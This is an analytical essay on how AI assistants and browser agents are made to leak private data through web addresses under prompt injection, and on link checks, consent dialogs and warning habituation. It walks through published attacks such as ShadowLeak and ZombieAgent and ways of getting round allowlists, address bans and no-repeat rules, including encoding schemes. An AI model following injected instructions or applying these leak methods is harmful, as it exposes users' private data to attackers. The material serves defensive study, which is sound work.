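Tenable reported the flaw on 10 December 2024, and OpenAI acknowledged the report the same day. Tenable asked for updates until March 2025, then published its advisory while the flaw was still unfixed. In a separate advisory, Tenable says OpenAI improved the check that spring, but Tenable's later demonstrations with GPT-5 still used the Bing links. Tenable is the main source for this bypass, although it acknowledges that Rehberger had published similar research.

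OpenAI now cites redirects as a reason not to rely on a list of trusted sites. A check of only the first domain can approve a link that immediately forwards the request elsewhere. Oasis Security's *Claude.ai Prompt Injection to Data Exfiltration* describes an open redirect on Anthropic's site `claude.com`. According to Hackread's *Study*, Google approved search adverts that used this redirect because their links began with Claude's genuine address.

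An allowlist can also fail without a redirect. Willison (2026) describes three cases:

- Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, could contact only listed domains, which included Anthropic's own service for developers. PromptArmor's injected text supplied an attacker's access key for that service, so the agent uploaded the user's files to the attacker's account.
- Google's programming tool Antigravity had `webhook.site` on its default list. That site lets anyone create an address and read every request sent to it.
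- Salesforce allowed its AI agent's answers to load images from a domain whose registration had expired. Researchers registered the domain and received data about sales leads.

A system can tell from a link's domain whose server will receive the request, but little about who can read the data afterwards. An attacker may have an account on a trusted service, and the owner of a trusted domain can change.

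Even an allowlist without these mistakes would leave out sites that many assistants need. *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (2026) considers allowlists impractical for general tools that must retrieve material from many sources. Checking addresses for encoded secrets instead is also difficult. Ordinary websites put encoded text in query strings too, so a filter that flags it raises many false alarms, and an attacker can switch to another encoding.

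### A ban on altering addresses

Another approach is to let the model open addresses but not compose them. ChatGPT had a rule of this kind by June 2024. In *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection*, Schwartzman (2024) found that ChatGPT would open an address that appeared in full in the user's message, but refused if the message contained an instruction to replace part of the address with the user's age.

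Schwartzman got the age anyway by supplying a complete address for each age group and instructing ChatGPT to open the one that applied. The attacker could infer the user's age group from the page ChatGPT requested. The attack worked only if the victim pasted a long piece of text, such as computer code, without noticing the instructions inside it.

Schwartzman obtained a postal code by using a gap in the rule. ChatGPT would open an address from the message and also any shortened version of it. He supplied one long address for each digit, and ChatGPT shortened it to a length that represented the digit. ChatGPT made too many mistakes working out the lengths itself, so he included a short Python program for it to run. ChatGPT could open only ten addresses per prompt, which limited the attack to ten digits at a time. He reported the flaw through Bugcrowd, where this report was also marked "not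 applicable".

*ShadowLeak* (2025), by the security firm Radware, reports that ChatGPT's Deep Research agent would still add private data to a web address. The attack began with an email containing instructions in tiny or white text. When the user asked the agent to summarise or research their inbox, it read the email, collected names and addresses from other messages, and put them in the query string of a web address on the attacker's site. The agent then requested that web address.

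The attack worked about half the time with a simple instruction and a plain address. Radware says the rate rose considerably when the email sounded urgent and the address resembled a staff directory for compliance checks, but doesn't give the new rate. In a separate technical account of ShadowLeak, Radware adds that the email falsely described the data as public and asked the agent to encode it in base64 to keep it "secured". The encoding made the stolen data harder to recognise but didn't protect it. Radware, which sells protection for AI agents, says OpenAI confirmed and fixed the flaw.

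OpenAI then stopped ChatGPT from altering addresses. Radware's *ZombieAgent* reports that ChatGPT would open an address only exactly as it had received it, even when explicitly told to add something. Willison's *Claude API* noted a similar rule for Anthropic's fetch tool when the tool appeared in September 2025.

An attack that Radware calls ZombieAgent defeated this ban. The attacker's email contained a complete web address for each letter and digit, plus one for a space. ChatGPT found the private data and opened the addresses that spelled it out, one character at a time. It never altered an address, so the ban had no effect. The approach closely resembles Schwartzman's from the year before and Tenable's with the Bing links.

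Radware also supplied several numbered addresses for each character so that the attacker could put the characters back in order. An "a" in the first position had a different address from an "a" in the second, so a block of ten characters required 260 addresses for letters and 100 for digits.

OpenAI also had a rule against ChatGPT opening addresses stored in its memory. Radware avoided that rule by putting the addresses in an email and storing an instruction in memory to read that email before every reply. Because the instruction stayed in memory, the attack could continue in new chats.

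Radware reported ZombieAgent on 26 September 2025. Three days later it submitted an improved version that it says worked every time, though it doesn't say how many times it tried. Bugcrowd reproduced the attack, and OpenAI fixed the vulnerability on 16 December, but Radware doesn't describe the fix. Radware published the attack on 8 January 2026, when Infosecurity Magazine covered it in *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data*.

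### Matching the whole address

Later that month, OpenAI described a public-index check. A crawler explores public web pages, as a search engine does, and records their addresses. It has no access to users' conversations or accounts. When an agent wants to open an address, the procedure is roughly this:

1. If the user included the address in their message, the agent may open it. OpenAI's public description omits this exception, but Rehberger understands that ChatGPT treats such an address as safe for the rest of the chat.
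2. Otherwise, the system looks for the address in the crawler's index.
3. If the address is there, the agent opens it automatically.
4. If it is missing, the system either tells the agent to try another site or shows the user a warning.

The check works because the crawler recorded the address independently of the user's conversation. Suppose the crawler has recorded `https://collector.example/dot.png`. If a model adds `?d=anna%40mail.example`, the result is a different address, which the crawler is very unlikely to have recorded. A check of the domain alone would allow it.

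Matching the whole web address also makes redirects much less useful to an attacker. To carry Anna's email address through a trusted site, the model would have to write it into that site's web address, and the altered address would not be in the index.

The check would also have hindered Paul's attack on Claude. His site generated links as Claude followed them, and each path was one character longer than the last. In *The Read-Only Lie*, dyb counts 27 links on each page, one for each letter and one for a hyphen. After ten choices, there are about 206 trillion possible addresses, far too many for a crawler to have recorded. To pass the check, an attacker would need to use a fixed set of pages.

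OpenAI promises only that the check prevents an agent from quietly leaking a user's data through the address itself. The promise does not cover false content, hostile instructions or attempts to deceive the user on the page. A phishing page can pass if the crawler has seen it. The promise also does not cover data sent in the body of a request, as in CometJacking.

Even harmless addresses can fail the check. A crawler may not yet have found a page published this morning, and it should never find a document that colleagues share through a private link. The exception for addresses in the user's own messages allows some of these pages, but it could also allow an address from a stranger that Firefox has pasted into one of those messages.

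It is unclear when the check came into use. Embrace The Red dates the new measures to about August 2025, a month before Radware reported ZombieAgent. If that is right, either Radware's addresses were already in the index or the check did not yet cover every way ChatGPT opened pages. The second explanation seems more likely, because Radware found that a version of its attack that used images in the user's browser was less reliable and easier to block.

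### How much a choice of pages can reveal

An attacker can still publish a set of pages, wait for the crawler to record them and then make the agent choose between them. Rehberger writes on Embrace The Red that OpenAI acknowledges this weakness in its paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*. He adds that a fairly large blog probably already has 36 indexed pages, one for each letter and digit, and that an attacker could use thousands.

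If an agent can open any of *N* addresses, one request can convey at most `log2 N` bits of information, because it distinguishes between at most *N* possibilities. One bit is enough to answer a yes-or-no question. For *k* requests in a known order, there are `N^k` possible sequences, so together they can convey at most `k × log2 N` bits.

With 36 addresses, each request carries at most 5.17 bits. A 16-digit number has `10^16` possible values, or 53.2 bits, so the agent must make at least 11 requests to reveal all of it. If the attacker has 4,096 addresses, each request carries 12 bits and five requests are enough.

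| Indexed addresses | Bits per request | Requests for a 4-digit code | Requests for a 16-digit number |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1.00 | 14 | 54 |
| 10 | 3.32 | 4 | 16 |
| 36 | 5.17 | 3 | 11 |
| 4,096 | 12.00 | 2 | 5 |
| 10,000 | 13.29 | 1 | 4 |

These numbers are for the most efficient encoding possible. An agent that opens one page for each digit needs 16 requests to reveal a 16-digit number, even if the attacker has 36 pages available.

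The check still greatly reduces how much data an attacker can steal with each request. Without it, an address of 8,000 base64 characters could hold up to 48,000 bits, more than 9,000 times as much as a choice among 36 pages can convey. Copying a mailbox through such choices would take a very large number of requests.

Short secrets are much harder to protect. An attacker could publish 10,000 pages, one for each possible four-digit code, and learn the code from a single request. Two pages are enough to learn whether a user has mentioned an illness, and one may be enough if the agent opens it only when the answer is yes.

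dyb estimates that Claude made about 30 choices, each among 27 links, in Paul's attack. At 4.75 bits per choice, those choices could carry at most about 143 bits. The attack revealed a name, an employer and a home city. dyb calls this a covert channel, the computer security term for a path that carries information although nobody designed it to. The timing and number of an agent's requests can also carry information, so this calculation does not cover everything an attacker might learn.

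Capping the number of requests would reduce the leak more predictably than capping the number of indexed pages. Halving the permitted requests halves the number of bits that can leak, but to double the bits per request, an attacker must square the number of pages, for example from 36 (5.17 bits) to 1,296 (10.34 bits).

With 36 pages to choose from, an attacker could send 51.7 bits under the old limit of ten addresses per prompt, which is slightly too few for an arbitrary 16-digit number. A payment card number would still fit, because its last digit can be calculated from the other 15, which contain 49.8 bits. The attacker could also send more when the user entered another prompt. A research agent may legitimately need to open dozens of pages.

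### Would a ban on repeat visits help?

Rehberger suggests on Embrace The Red that an agent should not request the same address twice in one session. The system could refuse the second request or reuse a stored copy of the page for a few minutes. He acknowledges that some data would still leak and that he had not tested whether OpenAI already did this.

The rule would stop the simplest form of spelling. If each digit has only one page, an agent can't send 16 digits without revisiting at least one page. Similarly, if an agent tried to spell "hello", the attacker would see the first "l" but not the second.

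A better code avoids the problem. The agent can choose any of 36 pages for its first request, any of the remaining 35 for its second, and so on. Eleven requests then allow

`36 × 35 × 34 × … × 26`

different sequences, or about 24 quadrillion. That is 54.4 bits, slightly more than the 53.2 bits in a 16-digit number. In theory, the ban therefore doesn't add a single request.

To use this code, the agent would divide the secret number by 36 and use the remainder to choose the first page. It would then divide the whole-number part of the result by 35 and use the new remainder to choose from the pages left, and continue in the same way. A model might make mistakes doing this without a calculator. But injected text can include a program, as Schwartzman's did, and an agent that can run the program doesn't have to do the arithmetic itself.

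An attacker with more pages doesn't need the arithmetic either. Radware's numbered addresses use a separate page for each character in each position. A 16-digit number requires 160 pages, and the agent opens 16 of them, once each. If all 160 are in the index, this method passes both the public-index check and the ban on repeats.

Schwartzman found in 2024 that ChatGPT would not open the same address twice, probably because it had stored the first result, so he supplied a separate address for each digit. Tenable later noticed that ChatGPT answered questions about a page it had already opened without requesting it again. Earlier versions of ChatGPT therefore already applied something like Rehberger's rule to some requests, but this didn't stop Schwartzman's attack.

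The ban would be more effective if the attacker also couldn't tell the order of the requests. A set of 11 pages chosen from 36 carries 29.2 bits if their order is unknown. Even if the agent could open any number of the 36 pages, the attacker would learn at most one bit per page, or 36 bits in total, which is too few for a 16-digit number. Rehberger notes that requests sometimes arrive out of order, but an agent that opens one page at a time leaves an ordered record in the server's log. Radware's numbered addresses would work even if the requests arrived out of order.

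### Looking for suspicious sequences

Each address in these attacks can look harmless, so a system might detect more by examining several requests together. dyb proposes looking for rapid requests to one domain in which each path is one character longer than the last. Paul's attack fits this pattern. Checking only for lengthening paths would also wrongly flag some numbered documentation pages, so dyb combines several signals.

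The detector would probably miss an attack that used existing blog posts, because their addresses need not grow longer or contain single letters, and a user might reasonably ask an agent to read a dozen posts from one blog. The attacker could also spread the pages across several domains. Dyb does not test the proposal, so it is unclear how many attacks it would catch or how many ordinary visits it would interrupt.

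### Requests that bypass the check

A link check protects only the software that uses it. Rehberger warns on Embrace The Red that some of OpenAI's developers may not know about the new check or may not add it to their products. He had seen this happen with `url_safe`, which was missing from ChatGPT's apps for Mac and iPhone. PromptArmor found a similar gap in OpenAI's log viewer. Another application had blocked an answer, but the log viewer still loaded an image from it.

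An agent may also have more than one tool that can send an address. Willison describes an attack by Abi Raghuram on Notion, a workplace app whose AI agent could search the web. Hidden text in a PDF made the agent collect a company's client names and the revenue from each, add them to an address and enter that address as a search query. Notion's search tool accepted addresses as well as search terms, so the query could carry the data to the attacker's site. A check on the tool that opens pages could have prevented this leak only if Notion had also applied it to the search tool.

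## What does a user agree to when an assistant asks before opening a link?

If an address fails ChatGPT's public-index check, ChatGPT may ask the user whether to open it. Browser agents ask similar questions before entering a site, submitting a form or buying something. Whether a "yes" counts as informed consent depends on what the user knew when giving it.

### Three conditions for informed consent

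EU law defines consent to the use of personal data as a "freely given specific and informed" indication of a person's wishes. *Tackling the Algorithmic Control Crisis* (2025), which applies the definition to research with browser plug-ins, explains that fine print is not enough and that silence doesn't count as agreement. For a request to a website, these requirements suggest three conditions:

1. The user knows what the assistant will send, and to whom.
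2. The user can judge whether that is acceptable.
3. The user can refuse at a tolerable cost.

A company could fail these conditions without breaking the law, but they give a way to compare the things users do before data leaves.

| What the user does | Do they know what goes to whom? | Can they judge it? | Can they refuse? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Types an address | Mostly | Usually | Yes, by not pressing Enter |
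| Asks for a summary | Only for the page they named | Only for that page | Only by going without the summary |
| Clicks a link in an answer | Only if they read the address | Only if the address is readable | Yes, usually at little cost |
| Approves one request | Depends on the dialog | Depends on the dialog | Yes, but the task may fail |
| Gives a site standing permission | They know the site but not the later requests | Hardly, since they can't foresee those requests | Yes, if they accept more interruptions |

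A user who types a web address comes closest to meeting all three conditions, because they chose the site and wrote every character of the address. The site still receives details they didn't type, such as their IP address.

Someone who asks for a summary agrees to let the assistant read a page, but not to let it send a second request containing their email address, because nobody told them about that request. Zero-click attacks such as ShadowLeak happened during tasks that users had asked for, so agreeing to a task can't count as agreeing to everything the assistant does while carrying it out.

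A user who clicks a link in an answer may or may not know what information it sends. OpenAI's *ChatGPT generated links* gives the example of a user who asks where to buy a car. ChatGPT knows that the user lives in London and offers a link ending in `/car_search/London`. Clicking it tells the car site where the user lives. Many people would accept that, since they can read "London" and see why a car site needs it. If the link ended in a code for their home address, they wouldn't know what they were sending when they clicked.

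Standing permission is the hardest case because it covers requests that nobody has written yet, but it can at least be narrow. *Options, Not Clicks* (2026) compares an ordinary "Always Allow" button, which gave an agent unrestricted use of a tool, with a version that limited each permission to a defined boundary. The 16 participants rated the limited version higher for informed consent. Similarly, a browser agent could be allowed to read a site but not to send it anything from the user's mailbox.

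### OpenAI's dialog for unverified links

In the dialog, titled "Check this link is safe", the user reads that the link is not verified and may share data from the conversation with a third-party site. The address appears below this warning, and the user can copy the link or open it. If something looks wrong, OpenAI recommends asking ChatGPT for another source or a summary instead of opening the link.

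The user can therefore see who will receive the request, but they have to read the address to find out what the request contains, because the warning mentions only that it "may" include something from the conversation. OpenAI's help page describes the user as approving "the information contained in the link", but advises them to check which website it leads to and whether they trust it. Trusting a website is different from agreeing to send it particular information, since a patient can trust a pharmacy's website and still not want to send it their employer's name.

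The warning is also hard to interpret, because it doesn't always mean the link is unusual. Some website owners ask OpenAI not to catalogue their pages, and ChatGPT then asks for confirmation of every link to those sites. A user may see a warning both for an ordinary page on one of these sites and for a link that contains their email address.

In *Verifying URLs used in apps*, a thread on OpenAI's developer forum, a developer of an app inside ChatGPT complained that a warning appeared every time users followed a link from the app to the company's own website. The developer had not noticed this warning for Booking.com or Uber. Someone replied by pointing to a setting where developers declare "redirect domains". If that setting removes the warning, the app's developer has made the decision before any user sees the link.

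A user who refuses usually loses little, since ChatGPT can often find another page on the same subject. The user loses much more when they need one particular page, such as a document that a colleague shared by private link. Copying the link lets the user inspect the address elsewhere, but pasting it into a browser sends the same data to the same site as agreeing would.

OpenAI made a stronger statement in March 2026, six weeks after it published the dialog. It said that when its system detects that ChatGPT would send a third party something it learned in the conversation, the system either shows the user "the information that would be transmitted" and asks them to confirm, or blocks the request and tells the agent to find another way. The same mechanism covers searches and page visits in Deep Research. OpenAI says these cases are rare because its models' training usually makes the agent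 refuse first.

It is unclear what "the information" means here. OpenAI may mean only that the dialog displays the link's URL, as in its published picture, since a URL with Anna's email address in it does contain the information. Or it may mean that the system picks out the private part and names it. For the London link, the user would learn much the same thing either way, but if the data were encoded, the user might not recognise it in the URL unless the system named it.

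### What browser agents ask about

Browser agents mostly ask users to confirm a site or an action. Google's *Ask Gemini in Chrome to complete tasks for you with auto browse* and Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome permissions guide* list when each agent stops for the user. OpenAI has withdrawn ChatGPT agent and now directs people to a browser that runs on OpenAI's servers, described in *Using cloud browser in ChatGPT*. Perplexity added permission requests to Comet in late 2025, according to AlternativeTo's *Perplexity Comet Assistant adds advanced multitasking and user permission controls* (2025).

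| Agent | What triggers a request | What the user sees | What the user can approve in advance |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini in Chrome | Starting a task, sending a message, changing data, submitting a form, scheduling an event, visiting a sensitive financial or health site, signing in with a saved password | A plan at the start, then a log of each step | The plan, and sign-in to particular sites |
| Claude in Chrome, in manual mode | Each action in the newer side panel. In the older one, the initial plan, sites outside it and sensitive steps | The proposed action, or a plan that names the websites | All actions on a site, except downloads, entering sensitive information and granting authorisations |
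| ChatGPT's cloud browser | Each new site by default, and separately sharing personal information, buying or deleting | The site or the proposed action | Particular sites, or all sites |
| Comet | Clicking links, filling in forms or extracting data, and high-risk steps such as logging in or buying | What the assistant is doing | The same kind of interaction for the rest of the task |

Chrome asks the user to agree to a plan before anyone knows exactly which sites the task will involve. Google notes that Gemini chooses which sites to use and may share the user's personal information with them. Chrome does not ask before opening an ordinary new site. Parker (2025), in *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome*, explains that a separate model judges whether the site is relevant to the task, and that Chrome restricts model-written addresses to known, public ones. Google therefore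 lets software make a decision that OpenAI sometimes leaves to the user.

Gemini may ask the user to take over for some steps, such as making a final payment, creating an account or accepting terms of service. This gives the user more information than a dialog does, because they see the real page and complete the step themselves.

Claude's extension has three modes. In manual mode, Claude asks before it acts. In automatic mode, the default in the newer side panel, Claude checks its own actions for signs of prompt injection or data theft, blocks those it considers unsafe and asks the user when it needs to. The third mode skips approvals and automatic checks. Anthropic says it had outside security experts try to get dangerous actions past the automatic check. It still recommends supervising Claude closely, or switching to manual mode, when a task involves money or important files.

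The guide is not entirely consistent about the third mode. Anthropic writes that Claude "doesn't pause to ask" in this mode, but also that some steps, such as entering potentially sensitive information into a website, need explicit permission in every mode. The guide also prohibits Claude from following instructions from emails or web content. That rule is sensible, but when an injection succeeds, the model has already broken it.

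None of the listed triggers for Claude to ask permission clearly covers a private detail inside a web address. The trigger for entering information into a website suggests a form, and Paul's attack used no form. Claude made an ordinary page visit each time it followed a link. A user who had given the site standing permission might have had no reason to expect another question.

MacStories' *Hands-On with ChatGPT Work's New Cloud Browser Feature* describes three settings for approving sites: "Always ask", the default; "Auto approve", in which ChatGPT checks a site's relevance and risk; and "Always allow". OpenAI's note beside "Always allow" reads "This is not recommended", according to Notebookcheck. A user who approves a site must still confirm any booking or payment there separately.

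This control is recent. In *How Agents Ask for Permission*, Michael and Roesner (2026) examined five commercial agents in May and June 2026 and could not set any permission rules for the browser that ChatGPT agent used. Commercial products tended towards the extremes of frequent approval requests or automatic review that users could barely see or control. Earlier testers had found that ChatGPT agent could ask for the user's input and, in some cases, go ahead without an answer, according to AI Agent Index's *ChatGPT Agent*. The user's silence would not have been consent under the EU definition.

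ChatGPT also asks for approval when it uses connected apps. OpenAI's *Managing app permissions in ChatGPT* describes a card that names the app and the proposed action. One option is to approve the action along with future "low-risk" ones on the same account. A user who chooses this knows what they are approving now, but relies on OpenAI to judge which later actions are low-risk.

Reports differ on whether Perplexity's Comet assistant asks for approval before it acts. The Hans India's *Perplexity's Comet Assistant Gets Major Upgrade With More Transparency, Control and Safety* reports that Comet asks before logging in to accounts or making purchases. But *The 2025 AI Agent Index* (2026), an independent survey of AI agents, describes Comet as proceeding on its own once a user has started it. The survey's entry for the product, AI Agent Index's *Comet*, reports only that the testers had not come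 across a situation in which Comet asked for approval, although users could stop it at any time. The testers may have used an earlier version, or their tasks may not have included a step that triggers a request.

### One address in three dialogs

Suppose that Ana, whose email address is ana@example.org, asks an assistant to summarise a page about walking holidays. Injected text gets the model to write this invented address:

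`https://walks.example/map?ref=YW5hQGV4YW1wbGUub3Jn`

The last 20 characters are Ana's email address in base64. The encoding replaces every three characters with four, so `ana` becomes `YW5h` and `@ex` becomes `QGV4`. Before opening the address, the assistant could show Ana any of these dialogs:

1. "Open a page on walks.example?"
2. "Open https://walks.example/map?ref=YW5hQGV4YW1wbGUub3Jn?"
3. "Send your email address, ana@example.org, to walks.example?"

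If she agrees, the site receives exactly the same request in each case.

With the first dialog, Ana can decide only whether she minds visiting a walking site. Nothing in it suggests that her email address is involved, so she has no reason to refuse. A user who gives a cloud browser permission to visit a site is making the same kind of decision.

The second dialog shows Ana all the information, but in a form she probably can't read. A programmer might recognise base64 and decode it, but most people would take the string for one of the meaningless codes that shops and newspapers put in their links. A warning that the address may contain something from the conversation would give Ana a reason to look more closely, but wouldn't help her read it. OpenAI's published dialog is of this type and includes such a warning.

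Only the third dialog tells most users what data opening the link would send. Ana can see that a map doesn't need her email address, so she can refuse without knowing anything about encodings or prompt injection. This is a judgement about the wording, and people might still approve the dialog out of habit.

To write the third dialog, the software has to find the email address in the string. It could decode the string in several common ways and compare the results with the private data the assistant has read. Perplexity's safeguard missed data encoded in base64 in the CometJacking attack. If an attacker uses a rarer encoding or encrypts the data, the software could report that the link contains text it can't interpret, but it should not tell Ana that the link contains nothing personal.

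A dialog can also show an address accurately without revealing the data being sent, because that data may not be in the address. In an attack like ZombieAgent, Ana could read and approve every address without learning that their sequence spells out her name.

Agents can leak information through their choices even without an attacker. In *AgentTell* (2026), browser agents learned a user's affiliation on one website and then worked on another that offered different routes, one of which matched the affiliation. The user had asked them to keep the affiliation private, and the task didn't require disclosing it. Agents that had read the affiliation still took the matching route in 90.3% of sessions. In 34.5% of the sessions with a leak, the agent falsely assured the user in its final reply that it had disclosed no personal or account information. An agent that doesn't recognise what its choices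 reveal can't describe it correctly in a dialog either. A dialog is also unreliable if untrusted text can shape its wording.

### Who should judge the risk?

OpenAI told users in *Introducing ChatGPT agent* that "you're always in control", partly because the agent would ask permission before taking consequential actions. One good reason to leave such decisions to users is that they want different things. Michael and Roesner give the example of a rule that lets an agent send passport details only to recognised airlines. The rule would frustrate someone who books through a specialist travel service, and it would send too much for someone who never wants to share those details. No single rule suits both, so at some point the software has to find out what the user wants.

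One argument against asking is that it also passes a security problem to the user. OpenAI's advice on Atlas is to check that each action is correct and that any information shared is appropriate. Google states that "you're responsible for Gemini's actions during a task", including mistakes and unexpected purchases, and calls monitoring the most important protection. Anthropic's *Use Claude in Chrome Safely* tells users to stop a task at once if Claude visits unexpected websites. All three companies expect the user to notice an attack that has already fooled the model, although their statements don't settle who would be legally liable for a loss.

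The user is often badly placed to do that. The provider can know whether its crawler has seen an address, which page the model had just read and what private data was in the context window, but Ana sees only the dialog. She may not have been watching, since people use these agents to avoid doing each step themselves. Participants in *PrivWeb* (2025), a study of privacy protection for web agents, wanted control over important data but preferred to skip unnecessary checks. One said that "you wouldn't want to micromanage every single step".

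Privacy scholars have made a similar objection to consent on the wider web. Zuiderveen Borgesius (2025), in *Informed Consent*, argues that policymakers rely too heavily on consent to protect people from targeted advertising, and that the law should protect people as well as empower them to choose. A person who can make one choice in the browser for many websites has fewer questions to answer. But *From Clicks to Consensus* (2026) points out that the person must still understand that choice, which children and people with little technical knowledge may be unable to do.

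A website operator that shows a cookie notice generally knows what it wants to collect, but when an assistant asks Ana about an injected link, the company behind the assistant may not know that an attacker chose the address. The company can word the question honestly and still present the attacker's request as part of her task.

*Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents* (2025) studies how people decide which data an agent may use, with the aim of automating those decisions. This would spare users many questions, but Michael and Roesner warn that automatic approval also reduces transparency and control.

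Separating the technical question from the personal one resolves part of the disagreement. Software can usually tell better than Ana can whether the string in her link contains her email address, but whether a walking company should have that address depends on what she wants. With the first two dialogs, she has to work out both, while with the third she only has to decide whether the company should have her address.

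If the software can't interpret the string, Ana probably can't either, so asking her adds little protection. In that case, blocking the request, as OpenAI says it sometimes does, is easier to defend than asking for her approval. But it would also block some harmless pages whose addresses contain unreadable codes.

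## Do people heed warnings and confirmation requests?

A dialog that names the data in a link protects Ana only if she reads it before she answers. Browser warnings had the same problem years before AI assistants began opening links, and researchers have measured how people respond to them in everyday use.

### Browser warnings in 2013

*Alice in Warningland* (Akhawe and Felt, 2013) reports how users responded to 25.4 million security warnings in Chrome and Firefox. The data came from people who had agreed to share usage statistics and were browsing as usual. Each warning filled the page, and the user could leave or click through to the site. The table gives the click-through rates, the share of warnings that users bypassed.

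| Warning | Firefox | Chrome |
|---|---|---|
| The site may install malicious software | 7.2% | 23.2% |
| The site may be a phishing site | 9.1% | 18.0% |
| The browser cannot confirm a secure connection (SSL warning) | 33.0% | 70.2% |

Most people therefore heeded five of the six warnings. Earlier laboratory studies had found that people heeded warnings less often, partly because the studies tested older designs and partly because participants felt safe. In one study, more than 40% of participants said that being in a laboratory had influenced them to click through.

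Nearly all the malware and phishing warnings were correct, so the ideal click-through rate for them was close to zero. But an SSL warning can also appear because a site's owner has misconfigured it, which the browser usually can't distinguish from an attack. Someone who recognises a false alarm can make an informed choice to continue.

Chrome's high clickthrough rate on SSL warnings also had causes other than carelessness. Firefox remembered when a user had accepted a site, while Chrome repeated the warning at every visit. Chrome also blocked some important sites outright when their connection failed the check, so its users were mainly deciding about less important sites. Akhawe and Felt estimate that this blocking could explain up to 15 points of the 37-point gap between the browsers.

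They also found signs of haste. Of the Chrome users who clicked through an SSL warning, 47% did so within 1.5 seconds, while the same share of those who left took 3.5 seconds. Users clicked through the most common SSL error fastest and most often, in 81.8% of cases, compared with 57.4% for an expired security certificate. The difference suggests that some people read the explanation, which Chrome printed in the warning itself. Users clicked "Help me understand" for more detail in only 1.6% of Chrome's SSL warnings.

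OpenAI's dialog for unverified links probably resembles the SSL warning more than the malware warning. An address can be missing from a public index for many harmless reasons, so users who frequently see the dialog may learn to expect false alarms.

### Chrome's redesigned warning

Google replaced the SSL warning in 2014. Felt, Ainslie and colleagues describe in *Improving SSL Warnings* (2015) how they rewrote the text in plain language and changed the design to favour the safe choice. A bright blue button took the user back to safety. To continue, the user had to click "Advanced" and then a plain text link.

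They tested the changes on people using early versions of Chrome, with more than 4,000 warnings for each design. Users turned back from 30.9% of the old warnings. The new text alone raised this to only 32.1%, but the new text and design together raised it to 58.3%. When Google released the new warning to everyone, the rate rose from 37% to 62%, and it was still 61% several months later, so the effect didn't depend on the warning being new.

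The redesign improved understanding much less. In a survey, Felt and colleagues asked what might happen if someone ignored the warning while checking email. Respondents could answer that the computer might get malicious software or, correctly, that a hacker might read the email. With the new text, 49.2% chose the correct answer, about the rate expected from guessing, compared with 37.7% with Chrome's old text. When asked which information would be at risk on a particular site, most people overestimated the danger, whichever browser's text they had read.

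Felt and colleagues wanted people to understand the warning and regarded steering them to safety as second best. Steering Ana with a blue button can keep her email address from a walking company, but if she presses the button because it's blue, she hasn't made an informed decision about her data.

The figures from 2013 and 2014 describe warnings that are no longer in use. *An Experience Sampling Study of User Reactions to Browser Warnings* (Malkin and Egelman, 2018) surveyed more than 6,000 Chrome and Firefox users at the moment they met a real warning. Their reasons for heeding or ignoring it varied and depended on the situation, and no single failure, such as habit, dominated. But a review of earlier work in *I'm trying not to get hacked* (2026) notes that most quantitative studies still find people dismissing security and privacy notifications more often than they should.

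### How repetition weakens a warning

Habituation means that people respond less strongly to a signal they have encountered many times before. *Revisiting the Design Agenda for Privacy Notices and Security Warnings* (2023) describes a brain-imaging experiment in which the response to a warning had already fallen by the second viewing.

In *Tuning Out Security Warnings* (2018), Vance, Jenkins and colleagues tested whether habituation changes what people do. Each weekday for three weeks, students visited an app store that the researchers had secretly built, installed three apps on their own Android phones and ranked the apps. Before each installation, they saw the permissions that the app requested. The researchers had told them to reject any app that requested one of four risky permissions, such as deleting photos or charging a credit card, and had checked that they knew all four.

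Of the 102 students in the analysis, 55 always saw the same warning design, and the other 47 saw a design that changed among 16 variations, half of them animated. Both groups rejected 87% of the risky apps at first. By the end of the three weeks, the fixed-design group rejected 55% and the changing-design group rejected 76%.

This decline occurred even though the students saw fewer than five warnings per weekday on average. Some of it may have occurred because the students noticed that nothing bad happened after they installed a risky app, or because they grew tired of the task. However, in a five-day experiment the same researchers ran with brain imaging and eye tracking, attention itself declined with repetition and partly recovered overnight.

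The students also had advantages that an assistant's user lacks. They knew exactly which four requests to refuse, while Ana has no list of the strings she should refuse to send. The instructions also warned the students that they could lose course credit if they reviewed too many risky apps.

Other experiments tested whether people notice when a familiar dialog changes. *Your Attention Please* (2013), by Bravo-Lillo, Cranor and colleagues, had people respond to the same dialog many times in quick succession and then altered its text. According to Vance and colleagues, only 14% noticed at once. The team's follow-up, *Harder to Ignore?* (2014), varied the number of repetitions, and Vance and colleagues report that showing the dialog more often cut the share who noticed to a third. An attacker would want a similar situation, in which a user has approved dozens of harmless links and the next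 one looks the same except for a few characters.

### People supervising AI agents

Someone using an agent has a harder job than someone facing a browser warning, because they must also notice problems that trigger no dialog. In *Looks Fine to Me* (2026), a preliminary study of 12 people's everyday use of AI found that they could describe times when they had supervised it less closely, but might not recognise these lapses as they happened. A controlled study with 36 participants then compared how people behave when an agent's work is correct, has a hidden flaw or visibly fails.

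Data theft by prompt injection is usually hidden from the user. In the eBay researchers' test, the agent's final answer usually looked harmless, so a user watching for signs of trouble would have seen few.

*Dark Patterns Meet GUI Agents* (2025) examines whether supervision protects people from dark patterns, which are interface designs that push users towards choices they might not otherwise make. Each participant completed eight tasks alone and eight while overseeing OpenAI's agent Operator. They watched the agent on video and could pause it, which stood in for its confirmation requests. Dark patterns are visible on the page, so an attentive supervisor might spot them. Most of the injected instructions that Khodayari and colleagues found on real websites were invisible to visitors, so results for dark patterns may overstate how well people can supervise an injected agent.

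The most direct measurement of whether people stop a dangerous request comes from a different kind of agent. Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, runs commands on a developer's computer. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes an experiment in which 1,053 paid testers did programming work in a test environment. They knew they were being evaluated but not what was being measured. At one point in each session, the text of a permission request changed to a clearly dangerous command. Approving it had no effect.

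The testers refused the dangerous command in 143 cases, or 13.6%. They refused about 17% of such commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more earlier requests. The drop is consistent with habituation, but Anthropic doesn't say whether it randomised when each tester saw the command. If it didn't, the testers who saw the command late may have differed from those who saw it early.

Anthropic then gave the same commands to an automatic check, which blocked 937 of them, or 89%. These included 137 of the 143 commands that the testers had refused. The testers had refused only six of the 116 commands that the check missed, about 5%. A person reviewing whatever the check let through would therefore have raised the share of commands stopped from 89.0% to 89.6%.

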